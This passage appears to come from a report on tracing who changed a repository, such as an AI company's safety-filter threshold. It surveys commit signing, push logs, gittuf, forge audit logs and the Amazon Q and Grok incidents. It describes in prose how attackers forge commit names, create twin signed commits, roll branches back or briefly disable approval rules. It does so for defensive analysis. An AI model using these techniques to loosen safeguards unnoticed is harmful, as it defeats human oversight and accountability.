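The fourth study, *Who's Pushing the Code?* (Zhang, Liang and colleagues, 2025), reports the share of commits without a signature, 56%, rather than the share with one. The researchers started with 9,810 GitHub repositories that had many stars and collected their contributors' commits from July to September 2022.

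The figures differ mainly because the samples contain different shares of work done through GitHub's website. In the data from Holtgrave and colleagues, GitHub itself made 73% of the signatures. In the extreme case of Redis, a database project, Sharma and Kancherla found valid signatures on 2,784 of 3,096 commits, or 90%. Once they removed bots and commits made on the website, only one of the remaining 312 commits had a valid signature, so the 90% figure is a very poor measure of the developers' own signing habits.

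The signing rate also depends on the age of the commits, since a commit that nobody signed in 2012 stays unsigned. The sample of Holtgrave and colleagues has more commits from 2015 than from any other year. GitHub introduced the "Verified" badge in 2016 and started signing commits made on its website in 2017. Sharma and Kancherla counted only commits made since April 2020. The high rate that Zhang and colleagues found is to be expected for recent work in popular repositories, where people often merge on the website.

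Signing rates also differ by field. Sharma and Kancherla studied 15 repositories from each of four fields. Leaving out bots and the website, developers had validly signed 28.35% of commits in security projects, 12.77% in web development, 5.95% in databases and 2.55% in machine learning. The machine-learning group included TensorFlow and PyTorch, two of the main libraries for building AI systems. These are public projects, and AI companies may sign more or less often in their internal repositories, but the figure gives no reason to assume that people in the field usually sign.

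The studies count different things. Mockus counted every signature without checking whether it was valid, while Sharma and Kancherla counted only those that GitHub accepted. Holtgrave and colleagues counted all signatures and then checked which ones GitHub had accepted, which included 82% of users' OpenPGP signatures. Counting only valid signatures from users lowers the 5.0% found by Holtgrave and colleagues to about 4%. The most common reason for rejection was that the signer had never given GitHub the public key, so an "Unverified" label often does not mean that the signer is an impostor.

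The individual developer's habits matter more to an investigator than these averages, because a missing signature is suspicious only if the named author always signs. Holtgrave and colleagues found that 2.0% of committers always signed, while 95.4% never had. Even strong supporters of signing forget to do it. When Nyall Dawson raised the idea of requiring signatures at QGIS, a free mapping program, a colleague pointed out that Dawson's own commits were unsigned. Dawson (2026) replied in *Requiring signed commits?* that he had once set up signing and must have forgotten to do so again when he reconfigured his computer.

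### Can anyone spot an impostor without signatures?

Since most developers don't sign their commits, researchers have looked for other ways to detect forged names. One is to compare the names on a commit with the account that pushed it. Holtgrave and colleagues did this for 437,211 commits pushed to 7,546 repositories between April and July 2024. The author, committer and pushing account were the same for only 30.1% of them.

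It is normal for a commit to name an author or committer other than the account that pushed it. Some GitHub repositories, for example, are copies that an automated account keeps up to date. Of the 7,546 repositories with push data, out of 50,328 in total, 85.9% had at least one push containing such a commit. This figure is better understood as the share of repositories in which a forged name would not look unusual, although the paper's summary presents it as the share of projects that attackers could abuse.

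A forged commit doesn't appear in its victim's own activity record, so Zhang and colleagues instead searched for commits that a repository's history showed under someone's profile but that were missing from that person's record. The method failed because ordinary pull requests leave the same pattern, and the researchers concluded that nobody can yet reliably detect impersonation from GitHub's commit histories.

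They also interviewed 17 GitHub users, but kept the answers of one former GitHub employee separate. None of the other 16 knew a person could commit under someone else's name. One believed a password and one-time codes protected him. The interviewers then demonstrated the forgery, using the participant's own email address if they agreed. Average concern about impersonation rose from 3.9 to 7.3 on a ten-point scale.

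The rise is unsurprising, since the researchers showed people an attack on their own identity and immediately asked how worried they were. The sample was also small, and ten of the 16 were students. The lack of prior knowledge is the more useful result. The six working engineers started less worried than the students, averaging 2.67 against 4.6, though the difference was not statistically significant. (The paper's description of its method swaps the members of the two groups, but the averages fit only if the six are the engineers.) If this holds more widely, the people most likely to read a company's change history may also be the least likely to doubt the names in it.

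### One signed commit with two hashes

Ginesin found in July 2026 that the same signed content can have more than one valid hash, because a commit's hash covers its signature. Someone without the private key can take a signed commit and produce a second version with a different hash.

This is possible because the same signature can often take more than one form. Verification checks whether a signature fits the contents and the key, but not whether it is the only one that would. Some signature schemes allow a second valid value that anyone can compute from the first. Some file formats leave room for notes that the signature does not protect, or allow two ways of writing the same number. In each case, an attacker can turn s into a different string s′ such that:

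- Verify(public key, m, s) and Verify(public key, m, s′) both accept
- H(m, s) ≠ H(m, s′)

The hash function correctly gives different results for different inputs, so replacing SHA-1 with a stronger function would not help. Ginesin found that GitHub accepted altered versions of every type of signature he tried and stored a separate "Verified" record for each. For one format, strict software on the user's computer rejected a version that GitHub had accepted. He reported the problem to GitHub in March 2026, and GitHub had not fixed it when he published.

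The second version of the commit has the same files, author, committer, dates, message and parents, because these are all part of m. An attacker therefore can't use the method to raise a blocking threshold or replace Ana's name with Ben's. A job that fetches the commit by its original full hash still gets the original. The attacker also needs a place to publish the second version, such as a fork or a repository they can write to.

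Only the newest signed commit can be replaced with a twin without breaking a later signature. If commit 2 gets a new hash, the parent line of commit 3 changes, so commit 3's signature fails, and so do all the signatures after it.

Still, the finding matters to anyone who treats a hash as the only name for a signed change. A company that blocks a malicious commit by its hash might let the twin through. An investigator might find one hash in a deployment record and another in the repository, and wrongly conclude that somebody had swapped the contents. Comparing the tree identifiers would settle this, because they are the same in both versions. The finding doesn't help a signer who wants to deny having made a change, because an attacker can only make a twin of a commit that someone with the key signed.

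### Checking signatures against a project's own rules

A project can check permission more directly if it keeps a list of the keys that may sign commits and lets everyone check commits against it. GNU Guix, a free system for installing and managing software, does this for its own updates, using a file in its repository that lists the keys of authorised developers. A commit passes if it was signed with a key listed in the parent commit's version of that file. An intruder therefore cannot add their own key and use it in the same commit, because a developer who is already on the list has to add it first.

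The chain needs a starting point, because an attacker could otherwise supply a whole false history with a false list of authorised keys. Guix users get two things from outside the repository: the hash of a first trusted commit and the identifier of the key that signed it. When they update, their own computers check every new commit after that one. Someone who took over the hosting server or a developer's account could still push commits, but users' computers would reject them unless the intruder also had an authorised signing key. GitHub's badge doesn't protect against this, because the intruder could add a new key to the stolen account.

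Guix requires the signer of a merge commit to be on the list of authorised signers in each of the commit's parents. Every other commit the merge brings in also needs an authorised signature, so a maintainer who accepts an outsider's patch has to sign it.

Sequoia git, a tool that other projects can adopt, works on the same principle but is more flexible. Its policy file can give one person the right to sign commits and another the right to sign releases or change the list. It accepts a version if it finds an unbroken path from a trusted starting commit to the newest one, in which each commit is authorized by the policy in the commit before it. A maintainer can therefore merge an outsider's unsigned work through a signed merge commit. The outsider's commits remain unauthenticated, but the maintainer vouches for the merged result by signing it.

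If a developer revokes a key because it was stolen, the dates on its signatures are no longer reliable, since the thief could have backdated new ones. Sequoia git then stops accepting any of that key's signatures, including the genuine ones. Maintainers can review the old commits and add those they still trust to a list of exceptions.

With such a system, a company could show that the key used to sign a threshold change was on its list when the change entered the history. But both tools authorise people for the whole repository. A developer allowed to fix a spelling mistake in the documentation would also pass the check after changing `block_above` from 0.50 to 0.90, so the company would need a separate rule for who may edit the file containing that threshold.

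## Who records the push, and who can alter that record?

A signature covers the contents of a commit, but a commit does not identify the branch it belongs on or the commits that came after it. Someone who controls the server can therefore mislead developers without forging anything. Suppose Ana signs three commits to a safety configuration:

| Commit | Change | `block_above` |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Creates the filter's settings | 0.90 |
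| 2 | Corrects a spelling mistake in a comment | 0.90 |
| 3 | Tightens the filter after harmful text gets through | 0.50 |

The `production` branch should point to commit 3, but a hostile server sends a newly installed machine commit 2 as the branch's latest commit. The machine downloads commits 1 and 2, successfully verifies their signatures and hashes, and runs the filter at 0.90. It cannot detect that commit 3 is missing, because neither commit refers to it. Only a computer that already had commit 3 would detect that the branch had moved backwards.

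Santiago Torres-Arias and colleagues described such attacks, which they called metadata manipulation attacks, in *On Omitting Commits and Committing Omissions* (2016). According to a summary of the finding by Yelgundhalli and colleagues, the server or anyone with commit access can point a branch to any commit in the repository, even if developers sign every commit and tag.

The substitute can also come from a different branch. Konstantin Ryabitsev, who manages kernel.org, the Linux kernel's hosting site, gives an example in *Signed git pushes*. A developer signs some dangerous test code and pushes it to a branch named to warn people not to use it. Someone else then puts the same commits on a branch that people use. The signatures are still valid, and the developer looks reckless. At an AI company, the test code could be an experiment with the safety filter turned off.

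To detect either attack, an investigator needs a record of where the branch pointed at each moment and who moved it.

### What forges record, and for how long

A company that runs its own Git server relies on the logs its server software keeps, and these may not cover every route into the server, as PHP's maintainers discovered. A company that uses GitHub has an audit log. According to GitHub's *Reviewing the audit log for your organization*, each entry shows the account, the action, the repository, the time and the country where the action originated. Entries also show how the user logged in if the action took place outside the website. Only the organisation's owners can read the log, and the documentation describes no way for them to edit it.

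The log covers the last 180 days, although another passage on the same page gives the limit as seven months. It keeps Git events, including pushes, for only seven days. Exports of these events also omit changes made on the website, so if Ben merges a pull request there, the branch moves but the export contains no push. Someone who discovers a changed threshold after two weeks would have to rely on GitHub's activity view or on a copy of the log the company had made in time. GitHub's public event feed would not supply the missing records, since it lacks even the forced tag moves of the Trivy attack.

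Large customers can make such a copy automatically by streaming the log to their own storage. GitHub's *Streaming the audit log for your enterprise* explains that enterprise owners can pause or delete the stream at any time. GitHub holds events for seven days during a pause, so after a ten-day pause the company loses the first three days of events. After a three-week pause, it loses all the events from that period. An owner could use a long pause to hide a push, although the gap in the stored files would be suspicious.

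When customers run GitHub's software on their own servers, they and their administrators have more control over the log. Enterprise owners choose how long to keep entries, and the software permanently deletes older ones, according to GitHub's *Configuring the audit log for your enterprise*. Owners can also choose whether the log includes pushes.

GitLab keeps saved audit events indefinitely, according to its *Audit events*, but *Audit event types* shows that these do not include pushes or the deletion of a merged merge request, GitLab's equivalent of a pull request. GitLab only streams both kinds of event to an outside destination, if the customer has set one up, so the record of who reviewed a change can disappear without a saved event. GitLab does save an event when an administrator starts or stops impersonating another user. An investigator should check for these events, because they could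 show that an administrator was acting through Ana's account.

| Record | Who can read or control it | How long it lasts |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub audit log, most events | Organisation owners can read it | 180 days |
| GitHub audit log, Git events | Organisation owners can read them | 7 days |
| Audit log on a self-hosted GitHub server | Enterprise owners set retention and can turn off Git events | The period they choose |
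| Streamed copy of GitHub's log | Enterprise owners can pause or delete the stream | As long as the company keeps it |
| GitLab's saved audit events | Project maintainers and group owners can read them on paid plans | Indefinitely |
| GitLab's push events | Whoever manages the stream and its destination | As long as the company keeps them |

On a self-hosted GitLab server, only administrators can manage the audit event stream for the whole installation, according to GitLab's *Audit event streaming for instances*. An administrator suspected of making a disputed change may therefore also control the evidence. A company can reduce this risk by sending the stream to storage that its GitLab administrators cannot change.

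### Turning off a rule for two minutes

Forges let a company protect a branch, for example by requiring a second person to approve each change. GitHub calls a group of such rules a ruleset. These rules are settings on the forge and are not part of the Git repository. According to GitHub's *Managing rulesets for a repository*, anyone with admin access to the repository can edit, delete or temporarily disable them.

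Suppose an administrator disables the approval rule at 14:00, pushes a commit that raises the blocking threshold at 14:01, and turns the rule back on at 14:02. Every copy of the repository receives the new commit, but none shows that the rule was off. Someone who checks the settings the next day will see that the branch requires approval and may assume that somebody approved the change.

Yelgundhalli and colleagues describe this method and say it evades detection. That is true of Git, but GitHub keeps a separate record. GitHub's *Managing rulesets for repositories in your organization* describes a history of changes to each ruleset over the last 180 days, which should show both changes in this example. People can also download an earlier version of a ruleset from this history, but the file omits the list of people who were allowed to bypass the ruleset.

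GitHub's rule insights page lists pushes that passed, failed or bypassed a rule. Since August 2026, organisations have also had a dashboard that shows the most frequent bypassers and exports the data (GitHub's *Rule insights dashboard generally available* (2026)). An administrator who used a bypass permission would appear there. But the page covers actions that GitHub checked against a ruleset, so a push made while the ruleset was off would probably not count as a bypass, and an investigator who relied on the page could easily miss it. The investigator would need to compare the time of the push with the ruleset's history before the records expire.

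### Signing the push

One remedy is for developers to sign the push as well as the commit. In December 2015 Torres-Arias, then writing as Santiago Torres, asked Git's developers about attacks that move references. Stefan Beller replied that push certificates ought to solve the problem. When Torres-Arias could not find documentation for them, King (2015), in *Malicously tampering git metadata?*, directed him to two technical files in Git's source code.

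A push certificate is a short signed statement about which references a push should move. It works like this:

1. Ben's Git program contacts the server, which sends a one-time value called a nonce. The server computes it from the current time and a secret.
2. The program writes the certificate, which includes the nonce, the server's address, and the old and new hash of each reference.
3. Ben's key signs the certificate, and the program sends it with the commits.
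4. The server checks the signature against its list of trusted keys. It can then store the certificate, or reject any push that lacks a valid one.

A certificate for moving `production` from commit 2 to commit 3 would look roughly like this, followed by the signature:

```
certificate version 0.1
pusher [Ben's key] 1772528700 +0000
pushee git.example.com:safety/config
nonce 1772528700-62ac09
[hash of commit 2] [hash of commit 3] refs/heads/production
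```

The certificate includes the branch and the server, so nobody can use it to justify putting the same commit on another branch. The nonce prevents an attacker from resending an old certificate. It also shows that Ben made the certificate for this server, but outsiders can't check this without the server's secret.

The old hash was missing from an early proposal. In a 2011 discussion of that proposal, a participant who signed as Sam (2011) pointed out that certificates would form an audit log only if they also recorded the previous commits. With both hashes, each certificate for a branch should start where the one before it ended:

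old hash in certificate *n* = new hash in certificate *n* − 1

If somebody removes a certificate from the middle, the hashes no longer match. Removing the newest one causes no mismatch, so a hostile server could still hide commit 3 and its certificate.

The server also has to support the feature. Ryabitsev wrote in 2020 that the vast majority of public forges had not turned it on. Linderud (2022) wrote in *Monitoring the kernel.org Transparency Log for a year* that GitHub did not support the server-side scripts needed to log certificates, but that GitLab customers could probably add them with some manual work.

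### The public log at kernel.org

Linux kernel developers have used push certificates since kernel.org began accepting them in November 2020, according to corbet's *Signed pushes for kernel.org* (2020). The site also publishes a log of every push to its public repositories. *Introducing the git transparency log* announced that the records went back to 2013 and that kernel.org immediately copied new ones to servers around the world. The log was still receiving entries in May 2026.

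Each record contains the account, the repository, the old and new hash of each reference, and a list of the commits in between. Its date is when the server received the push, so backdating a commit does not affect it. If the developer signed the push, the record includes the certificate.

Publishing the log makes it harder to rewrite unnoticed, because anyone with an earlier copy can see what changed. But publishing it does not ensure that a record was true when the server wrote it. The kernel.org document *Gitolite transparency log* warns that several kernel.org technical staff could fake a record, as could anyone who took over one of their accounts. It recommends that developers sign their pushes, since someone with access to the server would still lack a developer's key. However, kernel.org only stores the resulting certificates and does not use them to accept or reject pushes.

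In 2021 Morten Linderud, a developer of the Linux distribution Arch, built a program to check the log from outside. For each kernel release, the program looked for every new commit in his copy of the log and checked whether any push containing it had a valid signature. Between versions 5.16 and 5.17, it found all 14,199 new commits in the log, spread over 2,956 pushes. Only 2,239 of the commits, or about 16%, were in a push with a valid signature.

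Even this figure is generous, because the program counted commits as signed if one maintainer had signed a push to a personal repository, even if Torvalds later pushed them to the main one without signing. Linderud also said he did not fully trust his code. For an earlier release, version 5.11, the program failed to find 470 of 15,477 commits. Linderud doesn't explain why, but developers may have pushed some of them before November 2020, when the part of the log he monitored begins.

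Linderud argued more broadly that such a log is fairly useless unless somebody checks it. He would also have preferred a hash tree to the Git repository that kernel.org uses, because proving that a Git log contains a particular record requires working through the whole history. A hash tree combines records in pairs, then combines those pairs, until a single hash remains. Proving that one record is among a million then takes about 20 hashes (Linderud, writing from memory, guessed fewer than ten).

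### A push log inside the repository

gittuf, a security tool that Yelgundhalli and colleagues developed with help from industry, goes further by storing the push log in the repository itself. Its users download the log along with the code, and their own computers can check it. The log is called the reference state log, an idea that Torres-Arias and colleagues had proposed in 2016. According to gittuf's design document, each normal entry contains the name of a reference, the hash it now points to, a number and the hash of the previous entry. Whoever moved the reference signs the entry.

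The repository also contains a policy that lists which keys may change what. Unlike Guix and Sequoia git, gittuf can restrict individual files as well as branches, so a company could limit who may edit its thresholds. In simplified form, a policy for Ana's repository might be:

```
change this policy:         2 of {Ana, Ben, Chen}
branch production:          2 of {Ana, Ben, Chen}
file safety/filter.yaml:    1 of {Ana, Chen}
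```

Now suppose a production machine has already checked the log up to entry 7, which points `production` to commit 2. It then downloads two new entries. Entry 8 records that Ben has approved the next change, and entry 9, signed by Ana, points `production` to commit 3. A full check goes as follows:

1. The program goes back from entry 7 to the last entry that changed the policy. It checks that enough of the repository's owners signed that version, starting from a set of owners' keys that the machine already trusts.
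2. It checks that entry 9 contains the hash of entry 8, and that entry 8 contains the hash of entry 7.
3. It checks Ana's signature on entry 9 and finds her key on the list for `production`.
4. The policy requires two people, so the program looks for an approval from someone else. Ben's approval gives the branch, commit 2 as the starting point, and the tree identifier that the branch should have afterwards. The program checks that this matches the tree of commit 3. A second signature from Ana would not count.
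5. The program lists the files that differ between the two commits and finds `safety/filter.yaml`. Ana signed commit 3, and her key is on the list for that file.
6. It compares entry 9 with the branch it received from the server. Both should point to commit 3.

If the server shows commit 2 but leaves entry 9 in the log, the last check fails. Ben's approval includes the starting point so that nobody can reuse an old approval to move the branch back to an earlier version.

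A hostile server could still hide entries 8 and 9 together with commit 3. The machine would then receive a consistent but outdated history. Yelgundhalli and colleagues exclude this attack from the ones gittuf is meant to prevent, because developers talk to one another and would soon notice. This is reasonable for a team of people, but much less so for a machine that loads its safety settings overnight. The company would need to give that machine the number of the newest entry by some other route.

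Hiding Ana's entry from her colleagues is harder if the server lets them keep working. Their new entries follow entry 7, whereas Ana's computer has entries 8 and 9. The server cannot attach their entries to hers without her colleagues' keys, so Ana will see that the logs have diverged when she next downloads the log.

gittuf also makes it much harder to turn off a rule unnoticed. In this example a policy change needs two owners' signatures, and the log records it. Disabling a rule for two minutes would leave one entry for turning it off and another for turning it back on, in every complete copy of the log.

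Under the policy, gittuf allows any change that no rule covers. If Ben moved the blocking threshold to a new file without its own rule, the file check would not stop him, but the branch would still need two people's approval.

The log's order also helps when a developer replaces a key. gittuf checks each entry against the policy in force at that point in the log, so signatures from before the replacement remain valid, whereas Sequoia git rejects all of a stolen key's signatures. gittuf can accept the older signatures because it relies on an entry's position instead of its date, and a thief cannot insert an entry into a part of the log that other people already have. After withdrawing a stolen key, the owners still have to find and cancel any entries the thief added before the withdrawal.

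When a gittuf check fails, a developer adds an entry that marks the bad entry as invalid, then adds a commit that restores the last good files. All later changes to the same branch also become invalid, even if they followed the rules, because they build on the bad change. gittuf uses a new commit instead of moving the branch back because a computer that had already downloaded the bad commit might otherwise treat it as newer and keep it.

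gittuf does not yet do everything in its design. According to the design document, last modified in May 2025, it does not automatically check new entries from the server. It also ignores the expiry dates in the policy.

### Speed and storage

In an evaluation presented at the 2025 Network and Distributed System Security Symposium (NDSS), Yelgundhalli and colleagues added gittuf to copies of two large repositories, Git's own and that of Kubernetes, a system for running software across many computers. They created log entries for past changes and measured the extra storage and the time needed to check them.

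Storage grew by 0.70% to 3.62%. Checking only branch rules in Kubernetes took less than a tenth of a second per push. File rules were slower. With 30 file rules covering nearly 12,000 files, and more than 2,400 keys, checking both types of rule took 0.29 to 0.59 seconds per push, or nearly seven minutes for 1,000 pushes.

This overhead is small for a company that checks each push as it arrives. But the evaluation measured only computing overhead. The projects' contributors did not have to manage keys, wait for approvals or recover from a failed check, and that work may discourage a team more than an extra half second per push would.

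### Would it have stopped earlier attacks?

The same paper considers seven past attacks, including those on Linux in 2003, Gentoo in 2018 and PHP in 2021, and concludes that gittuf can protect against all of them. This conclusion comes from reasoning about each case, not from an experiment.

The paper attributes the PHP attack to a compromised server, an explanation that Popov withdrew. Its conclusion still holds for the real method of attack, because the attacker had two developers' passwords, which would not have been enough to sign an entry in the log. The malicious commits could still have reached the server, but anyone who checked the log would have found no valid entry for them.

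The other four cases are less well known:

- An unknown attacker added unauthorised code to the firewall software of the networking company Juniper.
- In 2010 someone broke into the repository behind the Free Software Foundation's website, and an automated system published the altered pages.
- In 2012 a security researcher used a flaw in GitHub to push a commit to Ruby on Rails, a popular toolkit for building websites.
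- Attackers took over the GitHub account of a contributor to Top.gg, a directory of chatbots for the messaging service Discord, probably by stealing browser cookies. They then added a malicious commit through GitHub's website.

In the Top.gg case, the attackers needed only a stolen session to add a commit through the website. They do not seem to have had the developer's own keys, which they would have needed to create a gittuf entry.

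The website case most resembles an AI safety configuration that takes effect as soon as someone changes it. Yelgundhalli and colleagues argue that the automated system could have checked the policy and refused to publish the pages. This works only if the check runs on the machine that puts the change into effect. The moved tags at tj-actions and Trivy, which are not among the seven cases, would also have lacked valid entries if the attackers had no authorised signing key. But GitHub Actions does not check for such entries, so each affected project would have had to add its own check.

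### How widely do people use it?

In June 2025 the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), an industry group, moved gittuf from its sandbox stage to its incubating stage, which is for more established projects. OpenSSF's *From Sandbox to Incubating* (2025) also reported that gittuf had reached beta. The NDSS paper describes a trial at the financial data company Bloomberg and use by several open-source projects, including gittuf itself. Debian, a Linux distribution, now includes version 0.12.0 in its development branch.

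gittuf is still in early adoption. A developer who pushes with ordinary Git adds no entries to gittuf's log, so a team gets full protection only if everyone who pushes uses gittuf. There is no public evidence that a major AI company uses it to protect its safety configuration. Most companies that want to know who moved a branch still depend on their forge's records.

### Stolen keys, collusion and unread logs

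A thief who has Ana's signing key can create entries that look exactly like hers. Requiring signatures from two people makes this harder. Suppose three developers each have a 1% chance of having their key stolen in a given year, and the thefts are independent. The chance that a thief gets at least one key is 1 − 0.99³, or about 3%. The chance of getting at least two is 3 × 0.01² × 0.99 + 0.01³, or about 0.03%, which is about a hundred times lower.

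The thefts may not be independent, however. If all three developers install the same malicious program, or let the same compromised coding agent use their keys, one attack could produce two valid signatures on a change that neither key holder had seen.

Two authorised people can also agree to make a harmful change. Yelgundhalli and colleagues point out that a single honest user can detect a policy violation, but a change signed by the required number of people is not a violation. gittuf also accepts a weaker policy if the required number of owners signs it. Other users can see the change and who signed it, which may deter people who expect someone to look.

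In many cases nobody will check the push log. The kernel.org log had been public for months before Linderud started monitoring it, and most of the commits he checked had no valid push signature. A company can avoid relying on volunteers by setting its production machines to reject any safety configuration that fails the check and to alert someone outside the team when that happens.

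## What is publicly known about who changes AI safeguards?

An AI company's push logs and safety configuration are normally private, so outsiders depend on what the company publishes about them. OpenAI has explained in some detail who decides how strong its safeguards should be, but its governance frameworks contain much less about who can edit the settings that implement those decisions.

### Who decides and who edits

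Under the April 2025 version of OpenAI's *Preparedness Framework*, a Safety Advisory Group of company leaders from different departments recommends the level and type of safeguards a model needs before release. OpenAI's leadership approves or rejects the recommendation, and a committee of the board oversees the decision.

These are decisions about policy. Suppose the group recommends a filter that blocks nearly all requests for help with biological weapons, and the leadership agrees. An engineer still has to turn that into a number, such as `block_above: 0.50`, and another engineer may want to raise the number six months later because the filter produces too many false alarms. An investigator could learn from the framework who should have approved the policy, but not who could edit the file or whether the later change needed a new approval.

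OpenAI's *Frontier Governance Framework*, from May 2026, explains how the company meets Californian and European rules for the most capable AI models. It lists controls on access to the weights (the numbers a model learns in training) of unreleased models, including approval by more than one person and detailed logs. It does not state who may edit a filter rule or a threshold, whether a second person has to approve the edit, or how long OpenAI keeps a record of it. Protecting the weights matters because a thief who copies them can run the model without OpenAI's filters, but a person can loosen a filter without access to the weights.

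In the same framework, OpenAI commits to documenting each covered model's risks and safeguards in a report. For models under the EU's AI Act, it will update the report if it has reason to believe that the basis for accepting the risks no longer holds. A much weaker filter could meet that condition, although OpenAI's examples are further training, riskier uses of the model and a serious incident.

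OpenAI also decides every six months whether to update the reports on its most capable models. It does not consider an update necessary if a model's capabilities have not materially changed. Raising a threshold from 0.50 to 0.90 changes what users can get from the system but not the model's capabilities. OpenAI could therefore leave the report as it is after such a change, unless someone there judged that the change undermined the original reasons for accepting the risks.

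OpenAI promises to publish material updates to its framework, with the reasons for them, in a changelog within 30 days. The promise covers the text of the framework, not the safety configuration.

Swipe Insight's *OpenAI Unveils Security Architecture for Frontier AI Model Training*, an undated summary of OpenAI's security measures, mentions that more than one person must approve code before it enters the deployment branch. It also mentions "infrastructure as code", the practice of describing servers and their settings in files instead of adjusting them by hand. If OpenAI kept its thresholds in those files, a single engineer could not have changed one through the normal process. But the summary doesn't state that the thresholds were kept there, and its reference to GPT-4, a 2023 model, suggests that it describes an earlier set-up.

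### Reviews before release and changes afterwards

OpenAI published *Managing frontier AI risk*, which covers its safeguards from research to public release, on 18 November 2026. According to EconoTimes' *OpenAI tightens model safeguards after security incident* (2026), models and their safeguards must pass a safety review before employees can use them, and again before release to outside users. EconoTimes does not mention any procedure for changing a safeguard after release. A review record shows which safeguards a model had on the day it passed, so if somebody loosened a filter a week later, the record would still describe the stricter version.

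Employees can flag safety incidents for possible public disclosure, and the Safety Advisory Group settles disagreements. An outsider would therefore hear about an unauthorised threshold change only if someone inside noticed it and the company decided to disclose it. The group also recommends the safeguards, so it might have to judge whether to publicise a failure of its own recommendation.

OpenAI's *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training*, published in September 2026, gives early guidelines for safety cases, which are structured, evidence-backed arguments about an activity's risks. Two of the guidelines would help with attribution. In the Chinese-language report *OpenAI发布AI训练安全准则*, 卜淑情 (Bu Shuqing) writes that OpenAI wants to keep unalterable records of what its AI agents do in training, evaluation and internal use, so that investigators can trace events later. Auditors would also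 get enough access to verify the safety case.

Such records could show that an agent edited a safety setting even if the commit named only a person. They would not help if a person had made the edit by hand. When OpenAI published the guidelines, it was still putting them into practice and expected to revise them.

### What an outsider can check

Most of these statements concern events inside the company, which the public cannot observe.

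| What OpenAI states | What an outsider can check |
|---|---|
| It publishes material changes to its governance framework | Anyone who saved an older copy can compare it with the new text and the changelog |
| Leadership approves or rejects the recommended safeguards | The published procedure, but not the individual decisions |
| Models and safeguards pass a review before each stage | Outside testers can examine the safeguards, but the public cannot see who approved them |
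| Access to unreleased weights is subject to controls such as multi-party approval and logging | Security auditors can test the controls, but the public cannot read the logs |
| Nobody should be able to alter the records of agents' actions | Auditors could check this if they received suitable access |

Outsiders can also test a safeguard directly. A researcher who sends a chatbot the same borderline requests every week may notice when more of them get through. That would be evidence that something changed and roughly when, but it would not show who was responsible or whether the cause was a new threshold, a new filter rule or a new version of the model.

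OpenAI's business customers can get a much better record of changes to their own settings. OpenAI's *Admin and Audit Logs API for the API Platform* describes a log of updates to a customer's organisation settings, changes in users' roles, and the creation and deletion of service accounts. Once a customer turns the log on, its administrators have to ask OpenAI's support staff to turn it off. An administrator who wanted to hide a change by turning off the log would therefore need OpenAI's help, whereas an enterprise owner on GitHub can pause the audit stream alone. The customer log does not cover changes OpenAI makes to its own safeguards.

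Even this log had a serious gap. OpenAI (2026) explained that in November 2025 it split one large service into several smaller ones and failed to set a variable that one of them needed to publish audit events, so that service's events were missing from the log. A separate fault disrupted the monitoring that should have caught the problem, and OpenAI had no alert for a drop in entries. It opened an incident on 19 February 2026, after customers complained, so the log may have been incomplete for about three months.

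In the PHP breach, the maintainers took missing log entries as a sign that someone had broken into the server. A customer reading OpenAI's incomplete log could have made the opposite mistake and concluded that nobody had changed a setting. An investigator can't safely draw either conclusion without knowing which events the log was recording at the time.

### Two incidents in 2025

Amazon Q Developer is an AI coding assistant available as an extension to the editor Visual Studio Code. In July 2025 an outsider put malicious code into the extension's public repository, and Amazon's release process automatically included it in version 1.84.0. According to AWS's *Security Update for Amazon Q Developer Extension for Visual Studio Code* (2025), the attacker used a GitHub token that had more access than it should have, taken from the configuration of CodeBuild, Amazon's service for building software.

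The malicious code reached users with the extension, but a syntax error kept it from running. Amazon replaced the token, removed the code and released version 1.85.0. The commit's route into the product is much clearer than its origin. AWS has not stated in the bulletin which names the commit carried, which account the token belonged to or who used it. A push log could have identified the account, but the token came from an automated build system, so the account might not have led to a person. Investigators faced the same difficulty with the stolen tokens of `@tj-actions-bot` and `aqua-bot`.

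The bulletin also omits the malicious commit's hash and how Amazon removed the code. Amazon may have used a revert, as Popov did at PHP, or a force-push, which could have taken the commit out of the branch's history. AWS did publish a hash of the 1.84.0 package, which lets users check whether they have the affected version but does not help identify the attacker.

Amazon changed its account of the incident within two days. In its original bulletin of 23 July, preserved on a note-sharing site, AWS wrote that researchers had reported that a "potentially unapproved code modification was attempted". It also said that the issue had not affected any end users. That may be true in the sense that the code never ran, but few readers would have guessed that Amazon had already distributed it. In the current version, updated on 25 July, AWS acknowledges that users received the code. The official page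 gives the date of the update but not the earlier text, so readers need someone else's copy to see what Amazon changed.

In May 2025 xAI announced that someone had made an unauthorised change to the prompt, or standing instructions, that its chatbot Grok followed on the social network X. The company's statement, quoted in VentureBeat's *Elon Musk's xAI tries to explain Grok's South African race relations freakout*, said the change was made at about 3:15 a.m. on 14 May and circumvented its code review. xAI did not disclose who was responsible, as Neowin's *Criticism leads xAI to open source Grok system prompts* (2025) pointed out. Bloomberg Law's *Musk’s xAI Blames Rogue Tampering for ‘White Genocide’ Glitches* (2025) quoted the company's promise of new checks on its employees. That promise suggests that an employee made the change, but xAI would have had the same reason to tighten those checks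 if an outsider had used an employee's account.

There appears to be no public case of someone using a forged commit to weaken an AI safeguard. AWS did not report a false name on the Amazon Q commit or a change to a safety filter, and it is unclear from xAI's statement whether the Grok change involved a commit. The lack of public cases is only weak evidence that this has never happened, because AI companies keep most of their safety configuration private and may not announce a forged commit if they find one.

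### Commits made by AI agents

When AI agents write much of a company's code, several of the five identities behind a change may be programs, and the commit can record them in different ways.

| Named on the commit | How this can happen | What remains unknown |
|---|---|---|
| A person | The agent used the Git settings on that person's computer | Whether the person wrote the change, read it or knew about it |
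| An agent | The agent committed under its own name | Who gave it the task, and with what instructions |
| A person and an agent | The agent added itself as co-author | Which of them chose the new value |
| A shared service account | An automated job commits work for many people and agents | Which person or agent was behind this change |

The commit message is also less informative. According to *Promises, Perils, and (Timely) Heuristics for Mining Coding Agent Activity*, agents often write commit messages themselves instead of asking the user. Suppose Ana tells an agent to reduce the number of complaints about a safety filter, and the agent raises the threshold and writes "Raise blocking threshold to cut false alarms". An investigator might read this as Ana's reason for the change, although she never mentioned the threshold. Only her instructions and the agent's session log would show how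 the decision came about.

Markers also don't show whether the developer reviewed a change closely or nobody read it. The same co-author line can appear on a commit the agent made entirely on its own and on one a developer edited first.

*Long-horizon autoformalization of a core theorem underlying MIP\* = RE* describes a project in which language models generated all the code, but agent-named accounts and co-author lines marked only 788 commits (28.4%) as involving an agent. Counting those markers would therefore have understated AI involvement in the project.

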